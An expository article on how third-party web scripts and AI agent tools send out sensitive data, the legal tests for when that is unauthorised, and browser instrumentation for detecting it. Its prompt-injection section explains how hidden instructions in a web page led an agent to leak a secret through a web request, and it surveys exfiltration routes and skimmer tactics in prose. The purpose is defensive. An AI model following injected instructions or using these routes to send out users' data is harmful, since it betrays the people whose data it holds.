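# Detecting unauthorised transmission of sensitive data by third-party web scripts and by AI agent tools

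## How web scripts and AI agent tools obtain and send sensitive data

Sending sensitive data, such as passwords, card numbers, contact details, health records or access keys, is unauthorised when the person or organisation entitled to decide has not allowed the recipient or the purpose. On the web, the usual sender is a third-party script, which is JavaScript that runs in a web page but comes from a party other than the site's owner. Site owners add such scripts for visitor statistics, advertising, customer chat and payment. AI agents can cause the same problem. An AI agent is a language model in a loop with software that carries out the actions the model requests. People give agents access to their mail, their files and their employers' databases so that the agents can do tasks for them.

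To detect unauthorised transmission of sensitive data, one has to know which data the software can reach and which channels it can use to send them. Both differ between a browser and an agent, though less than one might expect.

### The rights of a script in a page

Under the same-origin policy, a browser separates websites by origin, the combination of protocol, host name and port in a page's address. A site's encrypted and unencrypted versions have different origins, as does the same domain with and without the "www" prefix. According to *Loading web pages*, a chapter of WHATWG's HTML standard, parties that share an origin are treated as trusting each other and having the same authority, while parties with different origins are treated as potentially hostile. If a bank's page tries to examine the contents of a charity's page, the browser raises a security error.

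A script runs with the origin of the page that loads it, regardless of which server supplied the code. *Same-Origin Policy*, a chapter in the textbook for Berkeley's computer security course, CS 161, gives the example of a page on the course site that loads a tracking script from Google. The script runs with the course site's origin. An image from Google on the same page would keep Google's origin, and the page could read little more than its dimensions. If a shop embeds another company's script, that script therefore has the same access as the shop's own scripts in every customer's browser.

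A third-party script can look up any form field in the page by its name and read what the visitor has entered. It can also register an event listener, a function that the browser calls whenever something happens, such as a key press. Munir, Demir and colleagues (2025) describe in *Every Keystroke You Make* how the browser runs the listener before the event reaches the surrounding elements of the page, so the script can have each character before the visitor presses "submit". Listeners are common, and analytics scripts use them harmlessly to count clicks. Session replay services, which record a visitor's actions so that the site's owner can watch them later, rely on the same access.

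Man and Zitomer, in *6.4.3 & 11.6.1*, a set of slides on the payment card industry's security standard, add that a script can change the page, read the browser's local storage for the site and load more code from other domains. The browser does not isolate scripts on the same page from one another. Man and Zitomer also point out that a traditional site loads each page afresh, with only that page's scripts, whereas a shop built as a single-page application replaces the visible content without leaving the first page. A script loaded with the home page is therefore still running when the customer types a card number at the checkout.

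A frame, which is a page embedded inside another page, keeps the origin of the address it came from. If a shop embeds its payment provider's form in a frame from the provider's domain, scripts in the shop's page cannot read the fields inside it. Kosaka's *Same Origin Policy & iframe*, a Google exercise for web developers, shows this with one line of code. The line reads a secret message from a frame that shares the page's origin, but the browser blocks it when the frame has a different origin. Pages of different origins can still exchange messages through a function called postMessage, but only if both sides have code for it.

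The protection covers only what the visitor types into the frame. Man and Zitomer note that a script in the surrounding page can show a false payment form. A card number typed into that form is outside the frame and therefore unprotected.

### How data leaves a page

The same-origin policy restricts reading much more than sending. The World Wide Web Consortium's wiki page *Same Origin Policy* explains that a ban on sending information to other origins would also ban links to other sites, and there would be no web. A page may therefore send ordinary requests to any server. The browser usually withholds the reply from the script unless the receiving server permits access, but someone collecting data has little need for the reply.

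The main routes out of a page are these:

- A script can compose a request itself with fetch or the older XMLHttpRequest (XHR). The visitor stays on the page and sees nothing. Munir and colleagues note that a listener can pass a key press straight into such a request.
- A form can submit its fields to a server of another origin.
- A beacon is a small message that the browser delivers in the background, even while the visitor is leaving the page.
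- An image, often a single invisible pixel, makes the browser request an address, and whatever text the address contains goes to the server that hosts the image.
- A WebSocket is a connection that stays open and carries messages in both directions.
- Navigation to a new page, by a link or a redirect, delivers the text of the new address to the server at the other end.
- WebRTC, the browser's technology for video calls and direct data channels, opens connections of another kind altogether, and at least one web skimmer (a malicious script that copies payment details from a checkout page) has used it.

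Web pages can send data by many routes. MDN's *Content-Security-Policy*, from Mozilla's reference for web developers, lists seven script interfaces and link attributes under a single rule for outgoing connections. Sharma (2026), in *Intent to Experiment*, an announcement of a Chrome trial that lets sites limit their connections, also addresses redirects, the back and forward buttons, and several ways of telling the browser to prepare a connection in advance. She includes early lookups of a host's address too, because the lookup itself is network traffic. A detector that watches only fetch and XHR misses most of these routes.

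### One turn of an agent

A language model only produces text, so it cannot open a file or contact a server itself. The program around it, called the host, does both on the model's behalf.

1. The host assembles the context, the single sequence of text that the model receives. It contains the developer's instructions, the user's request, the conversation so far, descriptions of the available tools and the results of earlier actions.
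2. The model generates either an answer for the user or a tool call, which is a structured request to run a named function with particular arguments.
3. The host reads the tool call, checks it against whatever rules it has, and runs the function.
4. The host adds the function's result to the context and begins the next turn.

Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026), in *Silent Egress*, call this arrangement the reasoning and acting loop, and note that many deployed agents follow it. The context accumulates, so if the agent opened a file of access keys in its third turn, the keys are still there in the tenth unless the host has removed them, and the model can copy them into the arguments of any call. The host receives every tool call from the model before the call takes effect, and can record, alter or refuse it. Browsers give site owners no such single point of control over the scripts in a page.

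### Tool servers and the Model Context Protocol

Some tools are built into the agent. Others come from tool servers, which are programs that offer tools to agents and are often run by third parties. Agents and tool servers commonly communicate through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard. When its maintainers released the current version in July 2026, Model Context Protocol (2026) reported close to half a billion downloads a month across its main software kits. Automated builds download the same package many times, so this figure is a poor guide to the number of users, but the standard is almost certainly in wide use.

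In Model Context Protocol's *Architecture overview*, the host is an AI application such as a chat program or a code editor. It creates a separate client to connect to each tool server. A server may run locally, for instance to give access to files on the user's computer, or remotely on another company's machines, in which case every call sends data to that company. The host gets a list of tools from each server and merges the lists into one registry for the model.

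In an example from Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026), a server offers a tool named get_weather that takes a location. The model selects the tool, the client sends the server the tool's name and the argument "New York", and the server returns a line of text with the temperature and conditions. The client does not need to send anything else from the conversation. Model Context Protocol's *Architecture* (2026) includes the design principle that the full conversation stays with the host, and that a server should not be able to read it or see into other servers.

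The principle limits what the protocol shares automatically, but it cannot limit what the model writes into an argument. A tool that accepts free text, such as a search query or the body of a message, will also accept a password. The specification therefore recommends that clients show users the inputs of a call before sending it, to prevent "malicious or accidental data exfiltration", and that a human always be able to refuse a call. A client can ignore both recommendations and still conform to the standard.

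Data can also reach a server in ways that are easy to overlook. A server may answer a call by asking for more input, such as the user's account name, which the client collects and includes when it repeats the call. A server's author can also mark arguments to be copied into the web request's headers, where network equipment along the way can read them. The specification warns authors against marking passwords or keys.

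### How data leaves an agent

AI agent tools obtain sensitive data most directly through the arguments of tool calls, which go first to whoever runs the tool. That party may forward the data after the call, where the host cannot observe it.

An agent that can fetch web pages has a second way to send data, because the address it requests can carry data, as an image address does in a browser. This route is easy to misjudge because fetching looks like reading. A tool that runs commands in a shell, the text interface to a computer's operating system, gives the agent a broader route, because the agent can use any program on the machine that can open a connection. In a March 2026 post on the labels that servers attach to their tools, Model Context Protocol (2026) warned that a single injected instruction could cause any agent with unrestrained shell access to lose data, whether the shell came through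 MCP or was built into the host.

The agent's answer to the user can also transmit data. If the host displays images, an image address in the answer makes the user's device send a request as soon as the answer appears. A link does the same when the user clicks it. Neither involves a tool call, so a record of tool calls would not include the transmission.

The model provider is the recipient people most often forget. When the model runs as a remote service, the host sends it the context at every turn, including every file and message the agent has read. Users commonly accept this when they choose the product, but their employer or the people whose data are in the files may not have. Running the model on one's own machine, as Lan and colleagues did in their experiments, removes this recipient but leaves all the other routes open.

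### Prompt injection and the lethal trifecta

An agent that is able to send data can be made to do so by prompt injection, in which the model follows text in material the agent reads as if it were an instruction from its user. Simon Willison, who coined the term, took it from SQL injection, an older attack in which a database executes part of a user's input as a command (*The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, 2025). Both attacks exploit the mixing of trusted and untrusted content. The host joins the user's request and the text of a web page into one sequence, and models cannot reliably tell which part they should take instructions from.

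Lan and colleagues tested a prompt injection attack on their own experimental system. When the user asked the agent to summarise a page, the host automatically added the page's title, description and text to the agent's context. Instructions hidden in that material told the agent to make a web request containing a secret from the context. The secret left the system in about 89% of 480 runs, and in 95% of the successful attacks a check of the agent's final answer found nothing wrong. The model was small and the experimenters had placed the secret directly in its context, so the 89% is weak evidence of how often a current commercial agent would comply. The 95% matters more for detection, because an agent can leak a secret and still return a good summary two steps later.

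Willison's "lethal trifecta" is the three capabilities that together make such a theft possible: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and the ability to communicate externally. A mail tool can supply the first two, because it reads private messages and anyone can write to the user. Willison cites GitHub's official MCP server as an example that supplied all three. It could read public issues, which an attacker may have written. It could also open private repositories and publish changes where outsiders could see them. He lists attacks of this type on more than a dozen products since 2023, and reports that vendors fixed almost all of them promptly, usually by blocking the route by which data left. Nobody had found a way to make a model reliably ignore an attacker's instructions.

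Users who combine tools from several sources have no vendor to manage the risks of the combination. MCP's maintainers conclude that risk depends on the whole session rather than on any single server. Researchers demonstrated this with a malicious calendar entry, a calendar server and a separate tool that executed code on the user's machine. An unchanged mail search tool may be harmless in one session and used to steal data in another.

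The trifecta describes theft by an outsider who plants text, but sensitive data can also leak without all three of its conditions. A dishonest tool server can keep the arguments it receives. Even without an attacker, a model may include more personal detail in a request than the task requires.

### Borrowed authority

A third-party script acts with the authority of the site that embeds it, and an AI agent acts with the authority of its user. Lan and colleagues compare the agent to a "confused deputy", a term from older security research for a program that a less privileged party tricks into misusing its legitimate powers. The Agentic AI Foundation notes that tool servers can be in the same position because they often use their own credentials on behalf of many callers.

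Web scripts and AI agents differ in what determines their next action. A script follows code that an analyst can read and run again. Its supplier may later deliver different code, but each version is fixed. An agent's host program is also ordinary code, but reading it reveals little about what the agent will send, because the model's next request depends on everything in its context and may vary between runs on the same input.

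| | Third-party script | AI agent |
|---|---|---|
| Authority it borrows | The embedding site's origin | The user's accounts, files and permissions |
| Data within reach | Everything in the page outside cross-origin frames | Everything in the context, and whatever the tools can open |
| What determines the next action | Fixed code, until the supplier changes it | A model's output, given all it has read |
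| How an outsider gains control | By altering the script or the server that supplies it | By placing text where the agent will read it |
| Main routes out | Web requests, forms, images, open connections, navigation | Tool arguments, fetched addresses, shell commands, links and images in answers, the model provider |

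## When a transmission counts as unauthorised

Authorising a transmission means allowing particular data to go to a particular recipient for a particular purpose. Only someone entitled to decide about the data can do this. A customer who gives a shop her address for a delivery has allowed the shop and its courier to use it for that delivery. If the courier sells the address to an advertiser, the sale is unauthorised, even though the courier obtained the address properly.

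### Who can give permission

Several parties may have a say over the same data:

- A website's visitor decides about what she types, though she rarely knows which companies' scripts are on the page.
- The site's owner decides which scripts run, and can hire other companies to process data on the site's behalf.
- An agent's user decides about her own mail and files. She may also have access to data about colleagues or customers that she has no right to share.
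- An employer sets the rules for its own records, including which AI services may receive them.
- The law can permit a transmission to which nobody consented, such as a security check. It can also make a consent invalid, for instance if a company hid the request in small print.

American federal law generally lets someone intercept a communication if one party to it consents, while California requires the consent of every party. Munir and colleagues explain that this makes California's rule stricter for web tracking. A site owner's agreement with a tracking company may be enough under federal law, but in California the visitor has to agree too.

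Site owners do not always know what they have permitted. Senol, Acar and colleagues (*Leaky Forms*, 2022) used an automated browser to type email addresses into forms without submitting them, and found trackers collecting the addresses on thousands of websites. They wrote to 58 sites to ask why, and 30 replied. FiveThirtyEight, Trello and at least three others said they had been unaware of the collection and removed it. Eight of the companies that received the addresses, including Adobe, FullStory and Yandex, answered that they only processed data for the sites, and told the researchers to ask the sites. Data can therefore be collected without anyone having knowingly decided to collect it.

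### Contextual integrity

People seldom give explicit permission for each flow of data, so most judgements about authorisation rest on what they could reasonably expect. The philosopher Helen Nissenbaum proposed in *Privacy as Contextual Integrity* (2004) that a flow of information respects privacy if it follows the norms of its setting, such as medicine, banking or friendship. A patient expects her doctor to discuss her illness with a specialist but not with her employer.

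Five parameters describe a flow:

| Parameter | A visitor books a hotel room | An agent moves a medical appointment |
|---|---|---|
| Sender | The visitor, through the hotel's form | The agent, on its user's behalf |
| Recipient | The hotel | The clinic's reception |
| Subject (the person whom the data describe) | The visitor | The user |
| Type of information | Name, email address, dates of stay | Name, current appointment, preferred times |
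| Transmission principle | The hotel receives the data when the visitor submits the form, and uses them for the booking | The clinic receives what it needs to change the appointment |

The transmission principle is the condition under which information moves. For example, the subject may have consented, the recipient may have promised confidentiality, or a law may require disclosure.

Changing any one parameter can make an acceptable flow unacceptable. If the hotel's page also sends the email address to an advertising company, the recipient is wrong. If the hotel collects the address from a visitor who abandons the form, the recipient and the data are the same, but the transmission principle has changed. If the visitor books for a friend, the subject is the friend, whom nobody consulted.

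Contextual integrity works best where norms are old and widely shared, as in medicine. Session replay and AI agents are too recent to have such norms, so two reasonable people could agree on all five parameters of a flow and still disagree about whether it is acceptable. The parameters make the disagreement more precise, because anyone who objects has to say which parameter makes the flow unacceptable.

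### Four kinds of unauthorised transmission

In theft, the recipient has no legitimate role. Examples include a web skimmer that copies card numbers and an agent that follows injected instructions and sends its user's access keys to a stranger. The site's owner and the agent's user would object if they knew.

Tracking without consent is different because the site's owner has usually installed the software on purpose, but the visitor has not agreed to the tracking or has agreed to something narrower. Taboola, an advertising company, told Senol and colleagues that it collected hashed email addresses, which are scrambled but still identify a person, to personalise advertising and content. It said it did this only after the visitor consented, but the researchers' checks showed that it sometimes collected the addresses without first getting consent.

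Incidental collection happens when software picks up data that neither the software's supplier nor the site wanted. Session replay services usually try to leave out passwords, which they recognise by the form field's type. The filter can fail if a "show password" button turns the field into ordinary text. Senol and colleagues simulated this change and found session replay scripts collecting passwords on 52 websites. Yandex and Mixpanel released fixes after the researchers reported the problem to them.

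A tool or agent overshares when it sends data to the right recipient for the right purpose but includes more data, or other types of data, than the task requires.

These cases call for different responses. Nobody loses anything if a site blocks a skimmer's server. Blocking a session replay service would remove something the site's owner wants, so masking the password field makes more sense. A message that shares too much should still be sent, but with the excess data removed.

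### Hard cases

Many sites check whether a username is free while the visitor is still typing, which sends the name to the site's own server before the visitor submits the form. This transmission is authorised because the visitor chose the recipient and wants the answer, but a detector that counted every transmission before submission as a leak would report it. Senol and colleagues found a similar practice, verifying email addresses, when they examined a sample of transmissions to sites' own domains. They also note that a tracker can appear under a site's own domain name, so the address of a request does not always identify its recipient.

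Search suggestions are harder to judge when another firm supplies them. Munir and colleagues describe a Google search box that sites can embed. Its event listener is attached only to the search field, and it sends each piece of typed text to Google, which returns suggestions. A Yandex script in the same study responded to keys pressed anywhere on the page and sent Yandex the text and email addresses that visitors typed into forms. Both met the study's criteria for interception, and Google's search box accounted for nearly a fifth of the sites flagged. A visitor who sees suggestions appear can tell that her query is being read, though she may not know that Google receives it. It is reasonable to treat the transmission as authorised for answering the search, but that permission would not extend to building an advertising profile from her queries.

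A password-strength script can do its calculation inside the page, without transmitting the password. If it sends the password to its supplier, the visitor would still approve of the purpose, but another company now has a working credential that it did not need. That transmission should count as unauthorised unless the visitor knew of the supplier and agreed. The difference between reading and sending can also matter in court. Munir and colleagues report that, in a 2024 ruling on TikTok's in-app browser, a federal court noted that recording keystrokes purely on the user's device might fall outside wiretapping law.

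A site's owner chooses to use session replay software and may have good reasons. Marriott told Senol and colleagues that it used the data for customer care, technical support and fraud prevention. But visitors may not know they are being recorded. In a 2026 case before the Third Circuit, a federal appeals court, the plaintiffs alleged that a retailer's replay code captured what people typed even if they never pressed "submit". Recording clicks and scrolling for the site's own use is close to what visitors might expect, but recording text that they typed and then deleted is not. The owner's approval of the software does not mean that visitors have agreed to this.

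Suppose a user asks an agent to tell her insurer the date of her last dental check-up, and the agent emails the insurer her entire dental record. She authorised the recipient and the purpose, and she gave the agent access to the file, but her request covered only the date, so sending the rest of the record is oversharing. If the insurer had asked for details of a treatment, the necessary amount would be less obvious, and the agent would have to ask her or follow a rule.

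### Interception under California law

Courts have mostly considered these questions under the California Invasion of Privacy Act (CIPA), enacted in 1967 against telephone tapping. Its main provision, *Penal Code section 631* (Public.Law), applies to anyone who "willfully and without the consent of all parties to the communication" reads, or tries to learn, the contents of a message in transit. It also covers tapping a line, using information obtained by interception and helping someone else to intercept. According to *Website Privacy Lawsuits Under CIPA* on Mondaq, a site that republishes law firms' articles, plaintiffs can claim $5,000 per violation without showing actual loss, and businesses have faced thousands of lawsuits and demand letters.

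A plaintiff must first show that someone eavesdropped. In *Thomas v. Papa John's* (June 2025), the Ninth Circuit, the federal appeals court that covers California, held that a party cannot eavesdrop on its own conversation. Plaintiffs therefore argue that the script's supplier eavesdropped and the site helped. Mondaq's *The Ninth Circuit Briefly Speaks on CIPA Section 631* quotes a standard under which helping requires both knowledge of the conduct and a purpose of assisting it. A site owner who did not know what a script collected might therefore have a defence.

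The eavesdropper must also obtain the contents of a communication. Judges distinguish contents (the substance of a message) from record information, such as the time of a visit or the type of device. Mondaq's *California District Court Draws Critical Line Between Browsing Data And "Contents"* describes *Wiley v. Universal Music* (September 2026), in which a federal court dismissed a section 631 claim because the plaintiffs had only browsed and clicked, without typing anything into a search bar or form. Six days earlier, another plaintiff's claim had survived because it included search queries. Other judges in the same district take a broader view. In *Krzyzek v. OpenX* (January 2026), a case against an advertising company covered in National Law Review's *CROSS SITE TRACKING SURVIVES* (2026), the judge accepted full page addresses and button clicks as contents.

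The requirement that has most helped defendants is that the data be read in transit. In one case, an eating disorder clinic's website had a tracking pixel installed. According to Inside Class Actions' *California Court Grants Summary Judgment for Defendant* (2025), the plaintiff said it collected the addresses of the pages she visited, the time she spent on each, how she reached them, and actions such as button clicks. Judge Vince Chhabria agreed that page addresses were contents, as Wheeler's *Privacy Ruling Shows How CIPA Conflicts With Modern Tech* (2026) notes, but he still ruled for the clinic. According to MediaPost's *Web User Aims To Revive Wiretap Case Against Eating Disorder Site*, he reasoned that the data travelled to Meta in encrypted packets, which Meta's system had to reassemble before it could filter anything, so any reading came after the transmission had ended. Another federal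 court had reasoned similarly in April 2025 about session replay on an insurer's website. It found that the recorded events became readable only after the vendor stored and reassembled them, according to Inside Privacy's *Court Grants Summary Judgment* (2025).

On this reasoning, the details of a vendor's servers can decide a case, even though the same company receives the visitor's data either way. Munir and colleagues place the interception earlier, when the event listener receives a key press. A federal judge refused to dismiss a claim against a laser hair removal chain, finding it plausible that Google had read a customer's communications in transit (Law360, *Laser Hair Removal Co. Can't Shave Google Tracking Suit*).

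Some of the conflict arises because the cases had reached different stages. On a motion to dismiss, the judge assumes that the plaintiff's factual allegations are true, whereas at summary judgment the judge examines the evidence. The clinic, the insurer and the shoe company Converse all won at summary judgment. The claims against OpenX, the laser chain and the department store Bloomingdale's survived motions to dismiss, the last of them after an appeal. Plaintiffs have also won at trial under a neighbouring section on eavesdropping and recording, when a San Francisco jury found against Meta in 2025 over health information it had received from Flo, a period-tracking app.

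Consent is the remaining element. Munir and colleagues read the cases as requiring consent that is prior, specific and effective. Visitors must agree before the capture begins, so a banner that appears after the listeners have started does not count, and they must know that a third party may receive what they type. Plaintiffs in federal court must also show a real injury. In the Ninth Circuit's *Popa v. Microsoft Corporation* (2025), a dispute under Pennsylvania law about session replay on a pet supplies site, the plaintiff failed to show one because she identified no embarrassing or otherwise private information that the software had collected. *Ninth Circuit Dismisses "Session Replay" Lawsuit* (2025), on Eric Goldman's blog, quotes the court's comparison of the software with a store clerk who observes shoppers. The *Wiley* plaintiffs met the injury requirement even though their wiretapping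 claim failed. They alleged that the site tracked them after they had declined cookies, and the judge gave weight to the deceit.

The law remains unsettled. By September 2026 no California appellate court had published a decision on whether CIPA covers website tracking, and the Ninth Circuit's 2025 rulings on section 631 were unpublished, so they bind no other court. In *Doe v. Eating Recovery Center LLC*, Judge Chhabria of the Northern District of California called the statute's language "a total mess". On 30 September 2026 the governor signed a law that ends private suits against websites under CIPA's "pen register" provision, which concerns addressing data rather than contents. The new law takes effect in January 2027 and, as Mondaq's *CIPA Update* (2026) notes, leaves private claims under section 631 available.

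### Collection before submission under the GDPR

Under the European Union's General Data Protection Regulation (GDPR), an organisation that collects personal data must be open about it, state a purpose and have a legal basis. These requirements apply whether or not anyone intercepted a message. Senol and colleagues apply them to email addresses that a site or tracker collects before the visitor submits a form.

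An email address is personal data, and a hashed one generally is too. The site's owner and the third party are typically both responsible. They must tell visitors clearly what they collect, why, and who receives it. A statement that the site shares data with "selected marketing partners" is too vague. They must also use the data only for purposes compatible with the one it was collected for, so if a visitor enters her address to log in, a tracker must not use it to track her across websites.

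Online tracking and behavioural advertising require prior consent. A valid consent request for this kind of collection would have to name the companies, state the marketing purpose and say that the companies will receive the address before the visitor clicks "submit". Silence or a failure to opt out does not count as consent. A security firm that collects the address for an extra check could rely on another legal basis, provided that it meets the regulation's other requirements. Two scripts could therefore make identical network requests even though only one of them is lawful.

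The regulation also applies to companies outside the EU that monitor the behaviour of people within it. Fines can reach €20 million or 4% of worldwide annual turnover.

### Authorisation as a policy

A detector can log that a script read a form field and that the field's contents left the browser, or that an agent put a dental record into a tool call. The log does not include who agreed to the transmission, so someone has to supply that information as a policy, a set of rules about what may go where and under what conditions.

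Researchers who scan the web use very simple policies. Munir and colleagues counted captured keystrokes that went to a domain other than the site's own, and assumed there was no consent because the browser never interacted with a consent banner. They considered it infeasible to evaluate consent automatically across thousands of sites, and did not claim that the transmissions they found were unlawful. Senol and colleagues used lists of known trackers and counted a domain if it appeared on any of them. They acknowledge that this can produce false alarms and omissions.

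A website's operator can write a more exact policy, specifying for each form field who may receive the data and whether they may receive it before the visitor submits the form or gives consent. For an AI agent, part of the policy comes from the user's request, which usually implies a recipient and a purpose. The employer's rules can add to it.

A list of permitted destinations would catch a skimmer that sends card numbers to an unfamiliar server. It would miss a password that an approved session replay service recorded by accident, or a dental record that went to the right insurer but should not have been shared. To catch these, the policy must also specify what types of data each destination may receive, and how much.

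Even a detailed policy cannot show what a recipient later does with the data. Munir and colleagues typed a different email address into the forms on each website but never submitted the forms. They still received marketing messages at the addresses used on 50 of the sites. Many messages came from domains with no apparent connection to the site, and the headers did not show who had passed the address on.

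## Detecting that a script reads what a visitor types

A policy on who may receive a form field's contents is useful only if someone can observe what scripts do with that field. A script accesses typed data when it reads the field's text or detects which keys the visitor pressed. It transmits the data when the text, or something computed from it, leaves the browser.

Scripts often read what a visitor types without transmitting it, as when a script rates the strength of a password inside the page. A script that measures a page's speed may listen for key presses only to detect when the visitor starts typing. Registering a listener lets a script read key presses, but the listener may never run, or may run and ignore which key was pressed.

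Some detectors check only whether typed text is transmitted, not whether a script reads it. *Exposed* (2025) describes how Blacklight, a tool that scans websites for trackers, types prepared text into a page's input fields and looks for the same text in outgoing requests. Blacklight reports a match as "keylogging", although it has not observed any script reading the keystrokes.

Observing access also helps to identify the script responsible, which may not belong to the company that receives the data. In their crawl from Europe, Senol and colleagues found 1,844 websites where email addresses were sent to trackers. On 565 of these, no script from the receiving domain helped start the request. In the crawl from the United States, a script served by adthrive.com, an advertising network, sent hashed email addresses to Yahoo. A site owner who checked only the destination would look for a Yahoo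 script and might not find one.

### Replacing functions in the page

JavaScript allows code in a page to replace most of the functions that the browser provides. Researchers use this to put a wrapper around addEventListener, the function that scripts call to register an event listener:

1. An automated browser inserts the researchers' code into each new page before any of the page's own scripts run.
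2. The code keeps a private reference to the original addEventListener and puts the wrapper in its place.
3. When a script calls addEventListener, the wrapper records the type of event, the time and the call stack, which is the chain of functions that led to the call. The stack identifies the script.
4. The wrapper passes the call on to the original function, so the page works as usual. It can also hand the browser a modified listener that makes a note each time it runs.

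Munir and colleagues used this method without having to modify the browser. They recorded when each listener was registered and when it ran, the data it received, and the code of the functions involved.

The order in step 1 matters because a script that ran before the wrapper was installed could keep the original function and continue to use it. Each frame also has its own copy of the browser's functions, so the wrapper must be installed in every new frame before other code runs there. Jueckstock and Kapravelos (2019) noted in *VisibleV8* that automation tools could guarantee this order, but that Firefox and Chrome extensions could not at the time. Senol and colleagues built a trial browser add-on that detects attempts to read and send form data. Such an add-on would protect visitors directly, but it would face the same ordering problem if it relied on wrappers.

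Wrappers record only the functions that researchers thought to replace, and Chrome does not allow them to replace everything. Jueckstock and Kapravelos counted 5,755 functions and properties available to web pages in Chrome 64 and found that 21 could not be modified. One of the 21 was window.document, through which scripts reach the contents of the page.

A page can also detect a wrapper. A script that reads the text of a built-in browser function gets a standard notice that the code is native, whereas a wrapper usually returns its own source code. Wrappers can also appear in call stacks. Jueckstock and Kapravelos found an advertising script that wrote to the page differently if such a check failed, and a Yandex script that obtained clean copies of two functions from a new frame. Many of these checks are innocent tests of whether the browser's functions work properly, but they still matter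 for measurement because a script may behave differently when researchers are watching it.

### Breakpoints through the debugging protocol

A debugger lets a developer pause a program at a chosen point, called a breakpoint. Other programs can control Chrome's debugger through the Chrome DevTools Protocol. A conditional breakpoint includes a short piece of code that the browser evaluates on reaching the breakpoint, to decide whether to pause. Tracker Radar Collector, a crawler from the privacy company DuckDuckGo, uses this code to record the call stack and other details when a script calls a particular function or reads a particular property.

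Senol and colleagues built their crawler on Tracker Radar Collector and extended it to log each time a script read a form field that the crawler had filled in. Each entry includes the time, the text and the field's attributes. Unlike a log of event listeners, this log records a read regardless of what prompted it.

Scripts may act on events other than key presses. On 17 websites in the European crawl, a feature of Facebook's tracking pixel sent Facebook a hashed email address in a message meant to report a click on a submit button, although the crawler had not clicked one. Senol and colleagues believe that Facebook's script treated clicks on unrelated buttons as submissions. A detector that monitored only key presses would probably not have connected the script with the email field.

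Breakpoints leave the browser's functions in place, so a page that checks for wrappers finds none. Researchers still have to choose in advance which functions and properties to watch. The page may also detect that a program is controlling the browser. Jueckstock and Kapravelos found that 29% of the 50,000 most popular websites loaded content that checked for signs of automated browsers. Senol and colleagues made their crawler type at irregular speeds so that it would look more like a person.

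If a tracker recognises a crawler and collects less than usual, the study will underestimate how much the tracker collects from ordinary visitors. This problem affects every crawl, whichever method it uses to record access.

### Logging inside the JavaScript engine

Chrome runs scripts in a JavaScript engine called V8. A script can do arithmetic or rearrange text within the engine, but to read a form field, register a listener or send a request, it has to use the browser's native (non-JavaScript) code. VisibleV8 is a modified version of V8 that logs each use of native code. APNIC's *Monitoring JavaScript with VisibleV8* (2020) reports that VisibleV8's developers first tried wrappers, but modified the engine instead because the wrappers had gaps in coverage, were easy to detect and ran very slowly.

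VisibleV8 logs calls to native functions with one added statement, because V8 routes them through a single internal function. Its developers had to switch off an optimisation that would have bypassed this function. Reading a property, such as the text of a field, is harder to log because V8 has many shortcuts for it. Before running a script, V8 translates it into simpler instructions called bytecode. During this translation, VisibleV8 adds a logging instruction wherever the script reads or writes a property. It keeps only the log entries that concern the browser's own objects.

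Each log entry gives the function or property, the script that used it, the position in the script and the page's origin. Researchers do not need to decide beforehand what to look for. The log should distinguish a listener that read which key the visitor pressed from one that only noted the time. It may not contain the typed text, because Jueckstock and Kapravelos describe logging the arguments of function calls and the values that scripts write, but do not mention the values that scripts read. This matters little in a crawl, because the researchers chose the text.

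VisibleV8 uses no wrapper that a page could find, but the page could notice that scripts run slowly. VisibleV8 was 60% to 70% slower than ordinary Chrome on one set of browser tests, and about six times slower on a set that mainly tested the JavaScript engine. Jueckstock and Kapravelos expected that a script that timed itself to detect VisibleV8 would leave evidence in the log.

Running a modified engine also takes more work. The developers have to adapt their changes to new versions of Chrome, so they kept the changes to fewer than 600 lines. The original version ran without Chrome's sandbox. The sandbox limits the damage that a malicious page can do to the computer, so this version is more suitable for research than for everyday browsing. The project's website, *VisibleV8*, lists studies from as recently as 2026 that used or extended the engine.

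This kind of log covers only code that runs during the visit. If a script collects payment details only at the checkout and the crawler never gets there, the log will not show the collection. wspr-ncsu's *FV8*, a later engine that includes VisibleV8's changes, addresses this by forcing some otherwise inactive code to run.

| | Wrapper in the page | Conditional breakpoint | Engine logging |
|---|---|---|---|
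| What it records | Calls to the functions that researchers replaced | Use of the functions and properties that researchers selected | All use of the browser's native functions and objects |
| Change to the browser | None | None, but a debugger controls it | Modified JavaScript engine |
| What a page may notice | The wrapper's text, its place in the call stack, signs of automation | Signs of automation | Slower scripts, signs of automation |

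### Key listeners on 15,000 websites

Munir and colleagues used wrappers to measure how often third-party scripts intercept typing. They sampled 15,000 websites from a ranking of the million most popular, taking 3,000 from each of five popularity bands. The first band covered the top 10,000 sites and the last covered half a million, so popular sites are heavily overrepresented and the study's percentages may not hold for the whole million.

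The crawler ran from California and visited each site's home page and up to ten other pages, preferring pages with forms. The final set contained 125,355 pages and 312,741 different forms. The crawler moved the mouse, pressed navigation keys and filled in the forms with suitable made-up data, such as an email address or a phone number, but never submitted them. It also typed on the page outside any field, to find scripts that monitored the whole keyboard.

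A script counted as intercepting if it met three criteria, which the researchers derived from wiretapping law:

- It installed a listener for one of three keyboard events, called keydown, keyup and keypress.
- It captured what the visitor entered in real time.
- It shared the captured data with a third-party server.

The first criterion alone would flag a large share of websites. The study's abstract and conclusion give 38.52% as the share of sites with key listeners installed by third parties. The body gives 41.57% as the share with listeners for the three keyboard events, without specifying who installed them.

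Other numbers in the paper do not fit the explanation that the higher total includes the sites' own scripts and the lower one covers only third parties. One list gives keydown listeners on 51.56% of sites, which is more than either total, and another gives 38.89%, which is more than the lower total. Munir and colleagues do not explain the differences, so the figure is best read as roughly four sites in ten.

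Scripts met all three criteria on at least 3.18% of the sites, which is about 480 sites, or roughly one in twelve of those with key listeners. They most often sent ordinary text from form fields (2.09% of sites), followed by email addresses (1.09%) and phone numbers (0.15%). They sent passwords on 0.01%, which is one or two sites.

The gap between listening and sending was especially wide for some suppliers. Cloudflare's analytics script listened for key presses on 8.49% of sites, but the researchers found it sending typed text on only 0.10%. Yandex's scripts listened for key presses on 1.75% of sites and sent typed data on 0.80%. Google Tag Manager, which site owners use to add and manage other scripts, installed listeners on 67.11% of sites but never met the criteria. By default, it responds to events such as page views and clicks, but not key presses.

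Scripts that send data may send less than they can read. On one site, a script from Raptive, an advertising company, had access to nearly everything the crawler typed but sent only email addresses. Yandex's listener ran when the crawler pressed keys outside any field, but the script did not send those keys. A detector that reported every access would treat these scripts alike, although they sent quite different data.

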